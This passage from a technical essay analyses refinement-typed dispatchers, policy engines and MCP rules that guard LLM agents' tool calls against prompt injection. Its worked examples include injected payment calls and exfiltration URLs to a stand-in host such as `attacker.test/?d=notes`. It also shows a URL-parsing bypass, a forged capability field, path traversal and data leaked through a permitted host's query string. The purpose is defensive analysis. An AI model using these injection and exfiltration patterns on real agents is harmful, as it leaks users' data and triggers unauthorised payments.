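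The brand also disappears at run time. No code ever sets `__brand`, and the compiler erases the type, so the dispatcher cannot check whether a value went through `admit`. Code in any other module can use `e as Declared` to skip the test. Unlike Flanagan's casts, this cast generates no code and tests nothing. A value of type `any` can skip the test without a cast. The generated union of capability names has the same weaknesses because it also exists only during compilation.

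A JavaScript class with a private field, written with `#`, can mark its instances in a way that survives compilation. Code outside the class cannot forge the field, and the class can test for it before dispatching. The assurance then comes from a run-time check again, and the type is a convenience for programmers.

### Two tool calls, five checks

Most agent runtimes already have some checks on tool calls. To compare them, suppose the summariser has read the hostile page and the model emits two calls. The first is the undeclared `pay` call. The runtime also serves a billing skill, so `pay` is on the runtime's list of tools. The second calls `fetch_page` with the URL `https://attacker.test/?d=notes`. The manifest lists the capability for `fetch_page`, `net.egress`, but not the host.

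| Check | `pay` | `fetch_page` with the attacker's host |
|---|---|---|
| JSON Schema validation | passes | passes unless the schema restricts hosts |
| Schema-constrained decoding | passes | passes unless the schema restricts hosts |
| Registry lookup | passes | passes unless the registry restricts hosts |
| Policy engine (Cedar, OPA) | refused | refused if the policy restricts hosts |
| Refined dispatcher | refused | refused if the condition compares hosts |

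A schema can restrict hosts with a regular expression, but the same schema normally applies to every skill that uses the tool. Regular expressions are also unreliable for parsing URLs. The pattern `^https://.*\.example\.com` matches `https://docs.example.com@attacker.test/`. That URL leads to `attacker.test` because the text between `https://` and `@` is a user name. A refined dispatcher therefore needs a proper URL parser inside `cap`.

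Constrained decoding, the technique behind Anthropic's strict mode, should also rule out calls to tools that are not on the list. *Closed-World Resolution Against Tool Hallucination in LLM Agents* (Iyer, 2026) tested ten models with prompts designed to induce invalid calls. The models named nonexistent tools 34 times when they wrote plain JSON for a program to parse, and three times when they used an API that enforces schemas. Those three calls were all to a tool named `grant_admin` and came from two small open-weight models, Llama-3.1-8B and Ministral-3-8B. The API evidently did not enforce the list strictly for those models, so the runtime still has to check names.

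Iyer's check looks up the tool in a registry. It rejects a call if the tool does not exist, if an argument is undeclared or missing, or if a value has the wrong type or falls outside its permitted range. In the tests it stopped all 322 invalid calls, but Iyer acknowledges that much of this result follows from the definitions, since the program that classified the calls read the same registry. The comparison also assumes a runtime that executes every call that no check has rejected, whereas a dispatcher that looks up functions in a table already rejects unknown names.

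The `pay` call passes the lookup because the tool exists and the arguments are valid. Iyer argues that the lookup has to come before the permission check, which handles real tools that are off limits at the current step. The order matters in a refined dispatcher because `cap` has to return something even when the model invents a tool, such as `wipe_disk`. If `cap` maps unfamiliar names to the general capability `tool.invoke`, and the manifest includes that capability, the membership test approves a tool that nobody registered.

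A policy engine comes closest to the refined dispatcher. Open Policy Agent (OPA) and Amazon's Cedar evaluate written rules about who may perform which action on which resource. In Cedar, the summariser's network permission could look like this:

```
permit (
  principal == Skill::"summarise-fetched-html",
  action == Action::"net.egress",
  resource
) when { resource.host like "*.example.com" };
```

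Cedar denies any request that no rule permits, so it denies both calls. Metere grants that Cedar is stronger in that its evaluator is formally verified, while Metere's runtime is not. Metere considers both engines weaker in that neither provides a proof before deployment that the agent cannot issue a forbidden request. But a refined dispatcher doesn't provide that proof either, since it also rejects the `pay` call at run time.

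Cedar's verification covers whether the engine evaluates a policy correctly. A refinement type can also ensure that the runtime consults the engine before it runs a tool, if the dispatcher's condition becomes `{e : Envelope | permitted(policy, e)}`. An operator who already uses Cedar would probably gain more from this combination than from a separate membership test on the manifest.

The names-only Haskell and JavaScript sketches would let the second call through. Even a condition that includes the host does not replace ordinary validation, because the schema or parser should reject a number in the `url` field before `cap` runs.

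Some bad arguments pass all five checks. In *RubricRefine*, LeVine, Evers and colleagues (2026) describe an agent that passes `-pool` as a hotel preference to mean "without a pool". The booking function does not support this but runs without an error. Their system has a language model compare the agent's code with the tool documentation before anything runs. Across seven models, this raised the average success rate on one benchmark from 0.62 to 0.86. LeVine and colleagues say that a passing score is evidence, not proof, so it would be a poor basis for a security boundary.

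### What the Model Context Protocol requires

Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), part of the 28 July 2026 specification, requires servers to validate all tool inputs and implement proper access controls. Metere's dispatcher, by contrast, sits on the client side, between the model and the tools. The specification recommends, but does not require, that clients ask users to confirm sensitive operations and show them the inputs first, so a client that forwards every tool call without a permission check can still comply.

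A server may also vary its list of tools according to the credentials in a request. An operator could give each skill its own credentials, and the server would leave `pay` off the summariser's list. For remote tools, this is a serious alternative to a manifest check, although each server has to implement it correctly.

The protocol does not supply the information a refined dispatcher needs to compute `cap`. A tool definition contains a name, a description, schemas and optional annotations, but no field for the permission the tool requires. Clients must also treat the annotations as untrusted unless the server is trusted. The tool definition has no signature field, although Metere describes the protocol as shipping signed manifests.

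The July revision makes it more important to check arguments. According to the list of changes from Model Context Protocol (2026), it removes protocol-level sessions, so a server that needs to remember a shopping basket returns an identifier, which the model passes back as an ordinary argument. For servers that authenticate their callers, the specification calls such an identifier "a name, not a capability" and advises checking the caller's authorization on every call. A dispatcher that compares only operation names would not detect a call that uses another user's basket.

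Model Context Protocol (2025) defines two ways to report errors in tool calls. An unknown tool produces a protocol error, while a date in the wrong format produces a result with `isError` set to true. The previous revision clarified the rule for the second case so that models could correct their mistakes. The specification's examples of these errors don't include a call that is valid but forbidden, so the developer has to choose how to report one. Reporting the refusal with `isError` may lead the model to try again.

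A validator can also make network requests that bypass the dispatcher. This happens when a JSON Schema uses `$ref` to refer to another schema at a web address and the validator fetches it. The Agentic AI Foundation advises implementers not to follow network references automatically and to limit schema depth.

### A proof or a reviewed if-statement

A run-time test has to refuse the `pay` call in any case, so the proof is useful only for ensuring that no path through the checked code skips that test. This includes paths that rarely run. For example, an agent may resume after a human's approval only once a month, and a missing test on that path could go unnoticed for a long time. Run-time checking can miss errors on untested paths, as Flanagan, Freund and Tomb note in *Hybrid Types, Invariants, and Refinements For Imperative Objects*, and a review covers only the version the reviewer read.

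But a developer can avoid most of these risks with ordinary code. If the test is inside the dispatcher, as in `buildRefinedDispatch`, no caller can skip it, and the code to protect is only a few lines long. A reviewer can read it in a minute, a probe can try every capability name, and the build can require a passing probe and a second reviewer for any change to the dispatcher's file. Porting those lines to Liquid Haskell or F\* adds a second language and a new toolchain, and the proof still depends on the premises of Theorem 2.

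The reviewed if-statement is probably enough for a runtime with one dispatcher and a manifest of plain names. The proof is more useful when conditions involve hosts, paths or amounts, because tests cannot cover every value, or when approved calls pass through queues and retries before they run. An error in `cap`, which maps tool calls to permissions, undermines both the test and the proof, so that mapping deserves at least as much attention as the choice between them.

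## What the annotations must say, and who writes them

The proof for `handle` succeeds with any `cap` function and any manifest, including wrong ones. Whether the dispatcher refuses the right calls therefore depends on four things that people have to write down:

| Annotation | Example | Likely author |
|---|---|---|
| Capability vocabulary | `net.egress(host)` | the runtime's maintainers |
| Map from operations to capabilities | `fetch_page` needs `net.egress` | whoever registers the tool |
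| Declared set D | `net.egress(*.example.com)` | the skill's author, with a signer's endorsement |
| Conditions on arguments | a payment of at most 50 | the skill's author or the operator |

Metere writes that the type-checking step needs only annotations in the manifest. These annotations cover the declared set and any conditions inside it, but the vocabulary and the map have to exist first. A mistake in the map affects every skill the runtime loads.

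### The vocabulary

Metere's companion paper proposes nine capabilities:

| Capability | Effect |
|---|---|
| `net.egress(host)` | contact a host over the network |
| `fs.read(path)` | read files under a path |
| `fs.write.rev(path)` | write to a file in a way the runtime can undo |
| `fs.write.irrev(path)` | delete, overwrite or truncate a file |
| `tool.invoke(name)` | call a named tool |
| `spawn.proc(cmd)` | start an external process |
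| `publish(channel, …)` | post to an external channel |
| `pay(token, amount)` | transfer money or something else of value |
| `mutate.schema(target)` | change the structure of a database or configuration |

A reversible file write goes through a buffer, which holds the change in memory until the runtime commits or discards it. A write is irreversible if it bypasses the buffer or changes a remote object that the runtime cannot restore. An irreversible call may have to wait for a human's approval.

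The same operation can be reversible or irreversible. A `write_file` call needs `fs.write.rev` if the runtime buffers it and `fs.write.irrev` if it doesn't, so whoever writes the map has to know how the runtime executes each tool. If a developer later makes `write_file` bypass the buffer, the map becomes wrong even though the tool's name, schema and type stay the same.

The companion paper requires a runtime to tag every capability as reversible or irreversible, but it gives no tag for `net.egress`. A request that carries private notes to another server cannot be recalled, which suggests tagging `net.egress` as irreversible. That tag would require a prompt for every page that an unverified skill fetches.

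The nine entries are a minimum. A runtime can add others, such as `key.derive` for deriving cryptographic keys, and it rejects any manifest with an unrecognized name. None of the nine is specific to reading a mailbox or querying a database, so a runtime has to add an entry for these or fall back on `tool.invoke(name)`.

### Looking up what a call needs

The dispatcher has to get a call's capability from a table that the model cannot change. Suppose instead that `cap` simply returned a field of the tool call. The hostile page could then ask for one more line of JSON:

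```json
{
  "name": "pay",
  "input": { "token": "USDC", "amount": 500 },
  "capability": "fs.read"
}
```

The test finds `fs.read` in the summariser's declared set, so the payment runs. Metere's companion paper has the gate look up the capability for each call. The later preprint states the condition in terms of the envelope's "declared capability", which an implementer could misread as a field in the JSON.

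The same principle applies to any other fact a condition uses. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) describes a gate for tool calls that takes its facts only from real tool results and the user's messages. If the model writes that the user has approved a transfer, the gate ignores the statement.

Some operations need more than one capability. A `download` tool fetches a page and writes it to a file, but `cap(e) ∈ D` allows only one answer. If the map's author picks `net.egress`, the summariser's manifest approves the call and nobody checks the write. The function should therefore return a set, and the dispatcher's input type becomes:

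```
{e : Envelope | caps(e) ⊆ D}
```

Liquid Haskell can handle this condition, and Domínguez and Spiwack use the subset relation throughout their case study. The proof for `handle` has the same structure, with a subset test in place of the membership test.

The change does introduce a trap. The empty set is a subset of every set, so if the lookup returns an empty set for a tool it doesn't know, the dispatcher approves an invented `wipe_disk` call for every skill. The lookup has to keep "needs nothing" apart from "not registered":

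```haskell
capsOf :: Envelope -> Maybe (Set Cap)
capsOf e = case op e of
  "fetch_page"  -> Just (fromList [NetEgress])
  "download"    -> Just (fromList [NetEgress, FsWriteRev])
  "pay"         -> Just (fromList [Pay])
  "add_numbers" -> Just empty
  _             -> Nothing      -- refuse the call
```

The sketch again ignores hosts and paths. With them, the subset test has to mean that for every capability the call needs, some entry in D covers it, which is a quantified statement. According to *An Introduction to Liquid Haskell* (2017), liquid types do not generate quantified formulas, so that the solver can always decide the formulas it receives. A developer can put the matching into an ordinary function, `covered m e`, whose result the solver treats as a single unknown statement. Only code review and testing can then show that the matching is right.

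For tools on remote servers, the operator usually has to write the map, because the Model Context Protocol does not supply one.

### Conditions on amounts, hosts and paths

A payment limit is the easiest condition for a solver. For a limit of 50 USDC, a digital token worth about a dollar, the condition is:

```
token = "USDC"  ∧  0 < amount  ∧  amount ≤ 50
```

The lower bound keeps out negative amounts, which careless payment code might treat as a transfer in the other direction. Comparisons and sums of integers belong to linear arithmetic, which SMT solvers can decide. If the runtime adds a fee, the solver can prove that the sum of an amount of at most 49 and a fee of at most 1 stays within the limit. The Scala prototype of Bovel and colleagues has a smaller built-in solver that lacks a decision procedure for linear arithmetic, so the programmer may have to test the sum at run time.

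No solver can check that the tool and the condition use the same unit. If the tool counts in millionths of a USDC, an amount of 50 is a fraction of a cent. A limit in euros needs an exchange rate, which the runtime has to fetch. Ten payments of 50 also pass, because the condition checks each call separately and a limit on the total depends on earlier calls.

A host satisfies the condition for `*.example.com` if its name ends in `.example.com`. The leading dot excludes names such as `evilexample.com`. Solvers have theories of strings, so they can prove, for instance, that any name the program builds by adding `.example.com` to a prefix satisfies the condition. When the URL comes from the model, the program must parse it, put the host into a standard form with lower-case letters and no trailing dot, and then test the condition at run time. Metere's companion paper lists host-name tricks among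 the attacks that every runtime should test for.

A request that passes the test can still go to an unintended machine. The domain name system translates the name into a network address at run time, and whoever controls the name can point it at a machine inside the operator's network. A server at `docs.example.com` can also reply with a redirect to `attacker.test`, and many HTTP libraries follow redirects automatically. The runtime therefore has to check the address it connects to and send each redirect through the dispatcher as a new call.

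Paths are the worst of the three. Suppose the condition is that the path starts with `./.cache/`:

```
./.cache/page.html           inside the directory
./.cache/../notes.txt        outside it, despite the prefix
./.cache/latest/notes.txt    outside it if "latest" is a link elsewhere
```

A solver can correctly prove that all of them satisfy the prefix condition as strings. Removing `..` from the text fixes the second path. The third depends on symbolic links, file-system entries that point to other locations, and only the file system can resolve them. Links also make the textual fix unreliable, because if `latest` is a link, `latest/..` means the parent of the location it points to.

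If the runtime resolves a path and tests the result before opening the file, another process can swap a directory for a link in between. Metere leaves such races to the audit log, which helps little with reads, because a read changes nothing that a later comparison could detect. A better method is to open the file and enforce the limit in one step. On Linux, the system call `openat2` can refuse any path that leads out of a given directory. The refinement type then describes a file handle that this call returned, and the checker relies on the operating system to enforce the limit correctly.

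All these conditions limit a call's target or size but not its content, so a harmful message to an approved channel still passes. Metere acknowledges the same gap in the companion paper's audit check, which compares operations and targets but not what the agent wrote.

### Broad entries and over-declaration

A manifest entry such as `tool.invoke(run_report)` names a tool but not its effects. The tool might read a spreadsheet, email a customer or start a payment. Metere gives the example of a call that declares only `tool.invoke` and runs a script that fetches a web page. The map can partly fix this by also listing each tool's effects, so that `run_report` needs `fs.read` and `net.egress` too. For a tool that runs arbitrary shell commands, an accurate entry has to list nearly the whole vocabulary, unless a sandbox restricts what the commands can do.

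A skill's author can also declare too much. If D contains all nine capabilities without limits, the program still type-checks, but every registered call satisfies the condition and the refined dispatcher does no more than the unrefined one. Metere calls over-declaration "fine" because it is visible in the manifest, and operators can later compare the declared set with what the skill used.

This is too relaxed, because in the companion paper, once a signer has vouched for the manifest, the runtime approves the skill's declared irreversible calls without asking anyone. If the manifest lists `pay` unnecessarily, the runtime will neither refuse a payment nor ask a human to approve it, and the comparison may happen after the money has been sent.

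Authors also have a reason to declare too much, because a missing entry causes an error the first time the skill needs it and an unnecessary one never does. An operator can look for unnecessary entries by running the skill on test tasks, recording the capabilities each call uses, and asking about any declared capability that never appears. Somebody still has to judge the rare cases, since a skill that issues refunds twice a year may not use its payment capability in any of the tests.

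### Two readings of human approval

Metere's companion paper is inconsistent about calls outside D, and its two rules lead to two different types. The strict rule denies every such call, while the lenient rule sends irreversible calls to a "broker", which can be a human, a written policy or a remote service.

Under the strict rule, the type stays `{e : Envelope | caps(e) ⊆ D}`. The summariser's `pay` call fails the test, and nobody sees a prompt. If the skill needs to pay for something, its author has to change the manifest, get a new signature and start a new session.

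Under the lenient rule, the condition needs the alternative `∨ approved(e)`. Theorem 2 is then false as written, because a call outside D can reach a host API if the broker approves it. The operator who reads the approval prompt also becomes part of the trusted base, and Metere warns that operators under load approve everything. A tool call includes the model's stated reason, and after reading the hostile page, the model might write that the user asked for the invoice to be settled. The prompt should therefore show the operation and arguments first, and mark the reason as unverified text.

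The approval also has to apply to one exact call. If `approved` records only that a human agreed to a payment, the runtime can change the amount afterwards. A separate entry point avoids this and leaves the strict type of the ordinary dispatcher alone:

```
dispatchApproved : t:Approval → {e : Envelope | e = call(t)} → Result
```

Here t stores the call that the human saw, and the checker rejects code that dispatches a different call. The type does not stop the runtime from using t twice. Yu and colleagues' gate prevents this at run time by accepting each confirmation only once, so a retry after a failure needs a new one.

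Under the companion paper's rules, every irreversible call from an unverified skill goes to the broker, whether or not the manifest lists it. D therefore doesn't affect those decisions, and the condition for irreversible calls reduces to `approved(e)`. Reversible calls run through the buffer at every level, and Metere doesn't state in that paper whether D has to list them. An implementer has to settle this before writing the type. Keeping the strict rule alongside `dispatchApproved` seems the better choice, because reviewers can then find every exception by searching for that name.

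### Errors in rules from written policies

Many organizations already have written policies that a language model could translate into conditions. Yu and colleagues measured how this fails, using the 26-billion-parameter open model gemma-4-26B on the airline and retail policies of τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer-service tasks. Each rule attaches a named condition to a list of tools, and either forbids a call while the condition holds or blocks it until the condition holds. A gate tests these rules at run time without refinement types, but each rule serves the same purpose as a condition on the dispatcher's input.

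People still had to write 34 conditions for three domains, along with code to evaluate each one, a table of the arguments it reads and a table of the tools that can satisfy it. The model chose only which conditions to attach to which tools.

Five runs over each policy produced 79 candidate rules for the airline and 53 for the retailer. A static check then compared the candidates with the tools' schemas and the two tables. It found defects in 29 airline candidates (36.7%) and 7 retail candidates (13.2%):

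| Defect | Airline | Retail |
|---|---|---|
| The rule covers all tools and cannot be narrowed | 11 | 2 |
| The condition reads an argument that the tool lacks | 8 | 1 |
| No tool in the domain can satisfy the condition | 5 | 0 |
| The rule demands confirmation for read-only tools | 5 | 0 |
| The rule blocks the tool that would satisfy it | 0 | 4 |

The check repaired or rejected these. After a majority vote and the merging of many duplicates, 10 airline rules and 5 retail rules remained. No candidate was rejected for naming a tool that didn't exist. A larger commercial model also made mistakes. Six of its 91 candidates read an argument that the tool lacked.

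The last row of the table comes from a clause requiring the agent to authenticate the user before doing anything else. The model turned it into a rule that blocked every tool until the user was authenticated, including the two tools that perform authentication, so no conversation could have got past the first step. A refinement checker would accept this rule, because it proves only that the code tests the condition before the call. The checker could catch a condition that reads a missing argument, provided each tool's arguments have their own record type.

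Most of these defects make the gate refuse too many calls, which somebody will soon notice, but a missing argument can also make it allow calls it should refuse. In a second set of tests, on the prompt-injection benchmark AgentDojo, some rules forbade a call if its `recipient` was unknown. If a tool's target field had another name, the condition was false and the rule never applied. In the benchmark's Slack tasks, attacks succeeded through an executed call in 15 of 105 cases. A check that switched such rules to a broader condition reduced this to zero, but the agent's success on harmless tasks fell from 57.1% to 14.3%. A dispatcher has the same weakness if `caps` looks for `url` in a tool whose field is named `uri` and treats the missing value as harmless.

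Some rules are structurally sound but have the wrong meaning. A telecom policy required the agent to check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment. The compiled rule blocked payment requests while a bill was overdue, which is the only time they make sense. The team found this error by replaying the rules over recorded sessions of an agent without a gate. In sessions where the agent had completed its task, the rule would have blocked 47 of 49 payment requests. Replaying takes little effort for anyone who keeps logs, and it would work equally well for a new manifest.

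With the surviving rules, the share of state-changing calls that broke the policy fell from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the retailer. These figures cover only the clauses the team had encoded by hand for scoring. The airline agent also made a third as many state-changing calls, mainly because the gate refused so many attempts. Of the 40 violations that remained in retail, 21 broke two clauses for which the model had produced no rule, and nine were calls to an address-change tool that was missing from the confirmation rule's list.

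Part of the difficulty is that the policies themselves can be ambiguous. When another model judged a sample of 160 calls against the encoded clauses, it disagreed with the hand-written checker on 77. The team attributed 43 of these disagreements to interpretation, and 24 of the 43 concerned whether one "yes" from the user covers a single action or a whole batch. Letting one "yes" cover a batch lowers the airline's original violation rate from 66.3% to 36.8%. Whoever writes `approved(e)` has to choose between these readings, and the policy may not specify which one applies.

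Another option is to derive the permissions from each user request, as Progent does by having a language model write a policy for every task. Yu and colleagues compared Progent with their gate on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Attacks succeeded 46.5% of the time without a defence, 5.6% with Progent and never with the gate. Twelve of Progent's sixteen failures came from two requests to pay a bill, neither of which named the recipient's account, so the generated policy could not specify it. The gate blocked those attacks with a general rule about known recipients, but in one of the two tasks it also blocked the legitimate payment. The comparison covers only 16 user tasks, and the gate's developers ran it and wrote the banking policy.

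### What the types cost programmers

Someone must be able to write and maintain the refined signatures. For *Usability Barriers for Liquid Types*, Gamboa, Reese and colleagues (2025) interviewed and observed 19 developers using Liquid Haskell. Twelve were new to it and did a tutorial and then an exercise on queues, in sessions of up to two hours. The other seven had used it before, mostly in academia, and only one of them still used it. The study identified nine barriers, which fall under general developer experience, scaling to large codebases, and understanding what the verifier is doing. Because the sample is small and the method qualitative, the study shows what kinds of trouble occur but not how often.

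A dispatcher needs only a few refined signatures, so large codebases are less of a concern than understanding the verifier. The person whose edit breaks the proof will often have never written a refinement type. Liquid Haskell's syntax adds to the difficulty because it puts conditions in special comments, and Bovel and colleagues quote a study participant who remarked that people usually see comments as optional information.

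Bovel and colleagues' Scala prototype makes refinements part of the ordinary type system. They tried it on Fansi, a library of about 1,000 lines for coloured terminal text. One type for integers from 0 to 255 replaced three run-time checks inside a function, and the rest of the code compiled unchanged because every caller already tested the same bounds. Compilation took 407 milliseconds instead of 369, a difference they attribute to measurement noise. On the small benchmark programs, the overhead was mostly between 6% and 35%, in results they describe as preliminary.

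Fansi is close to the best case for a dispatcher because it has one short condition, which its callers already test. The map from tools to capabilities probably takes more work over time, and neither study covers it. Someone has to add an entry for every new tool and review it whenever the tool changes, and the compiler doesn't warn them if they forget.

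## What is guaranteed when the caller is a language model

People write the manifest and the map from tools to capabilities, and a type checker analyzes the dispatcher's source. A runtime normally samples the model's output at random, so the same prompt and web page may produce a harmless summary one day and a `pay` call the next. The guarantee about the dispatcher is still exact rather than statistical, because the proof doesn't depend on which calls the model is likely to make.

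### Every possible output

The verification condition for `handle` starts with "for every manifest m, tool call e and Boolean b". Since `handle` gets e by parsing the model's text, the proof covers every text that a model could emit:

```
for every text t:
  if handle(m, t) carries out a tool call e, then cap(e) ∈ caps(m)
```

If the model draws its text from a probability distribution P, the chance that the runtime carries out an undeclared call is the total probability that P assigns to texts that cause one. No such texts exist, so this chance is zero for every P. An attacker can change P by rewording a page the model reads, and a vendor changes it with every new model, but the chance stays zero and the same proof applies.

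Metere points out that safety training lowers the probability of a dangerous output without bringing it to zero. If an injected instruction works once in 1,000 attempts and agents read the attacker's page 10,000 times, the attacker can expect about ten successes. The attacker can also try other wordings to improve the rate.

The dispatcher's guarantee still holds only if its premises are true, and an attacker who finds a mistake in `cap` can exploit it every time. But the remaining uncertainty is about software and annotations, which people can inspect and correct.

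Theorem 2 in Metere's preprint holds "regardless of the LLM-side's behaviour", so it covers every output, however unlikely. The preprint makes this harder to see by modelling the LLM with a stochastic differential equation, the mathematics of a particle pushed about by random noise, and treating the resulting probability distribution as the right object to bound. The theorem uses neither the equation nor the distribution.

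### Robust safety

Cryptographers have long had to reason about a caller they cannot predict, because an attacker on a network can send any message. *Refinement Types for Secure Implementations*, by Bengtson, Bhargavan and colleagues, showed how a refinement type checker can handle such an attacker. Their tool, F7, checks programs in the functional language F#.

Programmers state their security goals in F7 with two commands. `assume C` adds the formula C to a log of accepted facts, and `assert C` claims that C follows from that log. Neither command has any effect when the program runs. A program is safe if no assertion fails in any possible run. In a dispatcher, the natural place for an assertion is just before the tool runs:

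```
assert (cap(e) ∈ caps(m))
```

The attacker, or opponent, is any program O that contains no assertions, since it could otherwise break safety trivially by asserting something false. O receives the functions that the checked program A exports. It can call them in any order and any number of times, run many copies in parallel, and choose each message after receiving the replies to earlier ones. A is robustly safe if, for every O, the combination of O and A is safe.

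Nobody can check every O individually, so Bengtson and colleagues introduce a type called `Un` for all data that an opponent can hold. A type is *public* if its values may flow to the opponent, and *tainted* if its values may come from the opponent. Take the type of file names that a program has permission to read:

```
{x : string | CanRead(x)}
```

This type is public because its values are ordinary strings. It is not tainted, because an opponent could supply a filename for which nobody has established `CanRead`.

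The theorem states that if A has type `Un`, then A is robustly safe. The proof is short once the type system is in place:

1. Every opponent has type `Un`, however it is written, because it contains no assertions and handles only `Un` data.
2. `Un` is equivalent to the function type `Un → Un`, so O applied to A is a well-typed program.
3. Well-typed programs are safe, so no assertion in A can fail.

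The checker must confirm that every function a module exports has a public type. A function type is public if its argument type is tainted and its result type is public. A function from text to a plain result therefore qualifies, but `dispatch` does not, because it accepts only tool calls with a declared capability and an opponent can produce others. F7 would reject an interface that exported `dispatch` to unchecked code. A developer who ports only the dispatch function to a verified language could easily make this mistake.

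The `handle` function in the earlier sketch takes a manifest as well as text. It should not be exported in that form, even though its type is public, because an opponent could pass in its own manifest that lists `pay`, and both the test and the assertion would succeed. The runtime has to supply the signed manifest itself and export a version of `handle` that takes only the text.

The model takes the opponent's place. The theorem applies even though the model is not an F# program. If the model's texts caused the runtime to carry out an undeclared call in some session, a trivial opponent program could cause the same call by sending the same texts in the same order, which the theorem rules out. Each random run of the model corresponds to one such program, so the theorem covers every run. It also covers a model that an attacker controls completely, or several models working together.

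A call can fail at run time without violating the theorem. In a file-access example, Bengtson and colleagues try to read a protected password file through a function that first looks up the file's permissions. The line type-checks "but dynamically fails", as they write in a code comment. The model's `pay` call also type-checks but fails at run time in `handle`.

### Fixed outputs and probabilities

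Some recent work on types for agents does restrict the model's behaviour. *λ_A* (Liu, 2026) translates agent configurations into a small typed language that treats a model call as a function from strings to strings. Liu proves that a well-typed agent either produces a value of the expected type or stops at a guard, which tests an output at run time. The Coq proof assistant checked the proof.

The theory covers only deterministic decoding, where the model's temperature is zero and each input has a single output. For random outputs, a model call would need the type `Str → Dist(Str)`, the type of a function that takes a string and returns a probability distribution over strings. Each later step in a pipeline would still accept an ordinary value but return a distribution, and the operator that joins two steps would have to combine their distributions. Liu leaves this to future work and argues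 that the deterministic case covers most production use, because 72% of the surveyed configurations that set a temperature set it at 0.3 or below. But a model at 0.3 still samples its output, and the configuration that opens Liu's overview uses 0.7.

Type safety probably doesn't need the restriction, because the proof's step for a model call requires only that the model return some string, and every sample is a string. The restriction matters more for Liu's equations, which let developers rearrange a pipeline without changing its output. With sampling, the same pipeline can give two different outputs even without rearrangement. The dispatcher's guarantee is closer to type safety because it doesn't depend on which string the model returns.

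A numerical guarantee, such as that fewer than one session in 1,000 will attempt an undeclared call, would need a model of the LLM's output distribution. Metere mentions research that treats language models as probabilistic transducers (machines that turn inputs into random outputs) and PRISM, a tool for calculating the probabilities of events in random systems. Metere decided against this approach partly because it requires a faithful probabilistic model of the LLM, which closed-weight models do not expose.

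Open weights would remove that obstacle, but the distribution also depends on the input, and the attacker writes part of the input. A rate measured on ordinary web pages is a poor guide to how the model will behave on a page designed to defeat it. Bounding the rate for every possible page would require another worst-case proof, this time about the model, which is far harder to analyse than a dispatcher. Measured rates are still useful for calls that the dispatcher allows, since the model's behaviour is often the only protection left.

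### The injected payment

The summariser's manifest does not list `pay`, so `handle` refuses the injected call to pay 500 USDC. It also refuses every later call to `pay`, whatever amount or reason the model gives.

Metere's formal definitions don't quite describe this result. A session has *capability containment* if every capability in its trace belongs to D, and the trace includes calls that the gate denied. The `pay` call therefore breaks containment as soon as the model emits it, even though no money moves. No dispatcher could prevent this, because a dispatcher acts only after the model emits a call. Metere still concludes that containment holds in every session, reasoning that undeclared calls never reach a host API. That conclusion would follow for the model's calls if the definition counted only calls that the runtime carries out, and operators should rely on that version.

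### Doing nothing, or never stopping

Theorem 2 is a safety property in the technical sense. It guarantees that a certain bad event never happens, but not that anything useful will. A model that ignores the user's request and emits no tool calls satisfies the guarantee, as does a dispatcher that refuses everything. Bengtson and colleagues note the same about their definition, under which a program that waits forever for a message nobody can send is safe.

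The abstract of Metere's preprint calls the model's freedom to refuse to act the only gap left by the verification scheme, and says that a run-time check at the end of the session catches it. That check compares changes in the outside world with the log of approved and executed calls. If the model does nothing, there are no changes and no log entries, so the check reports no problem.

An agent can also loop, perhaps fetching the same permitted page repeatedly. Each call satisfies the dispatcher's condition, and Metere lists unbounded resource consumption among the attacks that the methods do not eliminate. Liu proves that an agent loop with a limit of n steps ends after at most n steps, provided that each call to the model or a tool returns. The limit also caps the cost of a run, which is at most $0.20 for 20 steps with one $0.01 call per step. Liu's experiments count two calls per step,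 one to the model and one to a tool, which raises the cap to $0.40 if both cost the same.

Liu analysed 835 agent configurations from GitHub. In 88 of them, the analysis found neither a tool for ending the loop nor any other stopping mechanism.

### Permitted calls that do harm

Suppose the user has pasted some confidential notes into the conversation before asking for a summary. The hostile page came from a host under example.com, since the skill fetches from nowhere else, and its author may be able to read the request log of a server there. The page asks the model to put the notes into a web address:

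```json
{
  "name": "fetch_page",
  "input": { "url": "https://community.example.com/p?q=merger-closes-friday" }
}
```

This call needs `net.egress(community.example.com)`. The condition checks the host, which the entry `net.egress(*.example.com)` covers, so the dispatcher allows the call. Robust safety doesn't prevent the call either. In Bengtson and colleagues' system, a program may pass a value to the opponent only if the value has a public type. Here the model is the opponent, so the notes became public when the runtime put them into the model's input. To stop the call, the runtime would have to track where the text in the URL came from.

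The hostile page can also contain instructions for a harmful action within D. Suppose the company's billing system pays an invoice whenever someone inside its network opens `https://billing.example.com/pay?invoice=881`. Web servers are not supposed to change anything in response to a page request, but some do. The dispatcher would refuse a `pay` call, but it allows the model's `fetch_page` call to that address because it checks only the capability that the map assigns to an operation, and the map classifies this operation as a fetch.

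A skill that declares `pay` is exposed more directly. In Metere's companion paper, the capability is `pay(token, amount)`, which has no field for the recipient. A manifest can therefore limit a billing skill to 50 USDC per payment, but it cannot restrict who receives the money. A false invoice for 40 USDC would pass, and no human would see a prompt once a signer has vouched for the manifest.

Both calls are examples of the *confused deputy* problem, in which someone without permission to do something tricks a program that has permission into doing it. The name comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988), a "nearly true story" about Tymshare, a company that sold computer time. Tymshare's compiler had permission to write files in a system directory, where it kept usage statistics. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. One user gave the name of the company's billing file,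 which was in the same directory. Because the compiler had permission to write there, the operating system let it overwrite the billing records.

The operating system checked whether the compiler was allowed to write the file, when it should have checked whether the user was. GNU's *confused deputy* entry traces the problem to separating designation (what to act on) from authorization (permission to act). In the summariser, the hostile page designates the URL and the manifest authorizes the request. The dispatcher checks only that the skill has permission, and has no information about who wanted the call made.

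The refined dispatcher stops prompt injection from causing harmful actions, as Metere claims, but only when the skill hasn't declared those actions. An attacker can still use any permission the skill has, so a broad manifest lets a hostile page trigger more actions.

Object capabilities reduce the problem by combining the two parts. In Hardy's story, the user would have passed the compiler an open file instead of a name, and could have passed only a file that the user was allowed to write. Semgrep's *Security Like It's 1977* (2026) recommends such capabilities for AI agents and predicts that agents will make confused deputies more common. A runtime for the summariser could turn each address in the user's request into an identifier such as `page_1` and let `fetch_page` accept only these identifiers. An address on a hostile page would have no identifier, so the model could not fetch it.

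The agent could no longer follow links, which some tasks require. The method also helps less when the user has granted several permissions for good reasons. If a billing agent holds identifiers for 30 approved suppliers, a false invoice can still cause the model to pay the wrong one, although it can't add a new supplier to the list.

### How much a tool call can leak

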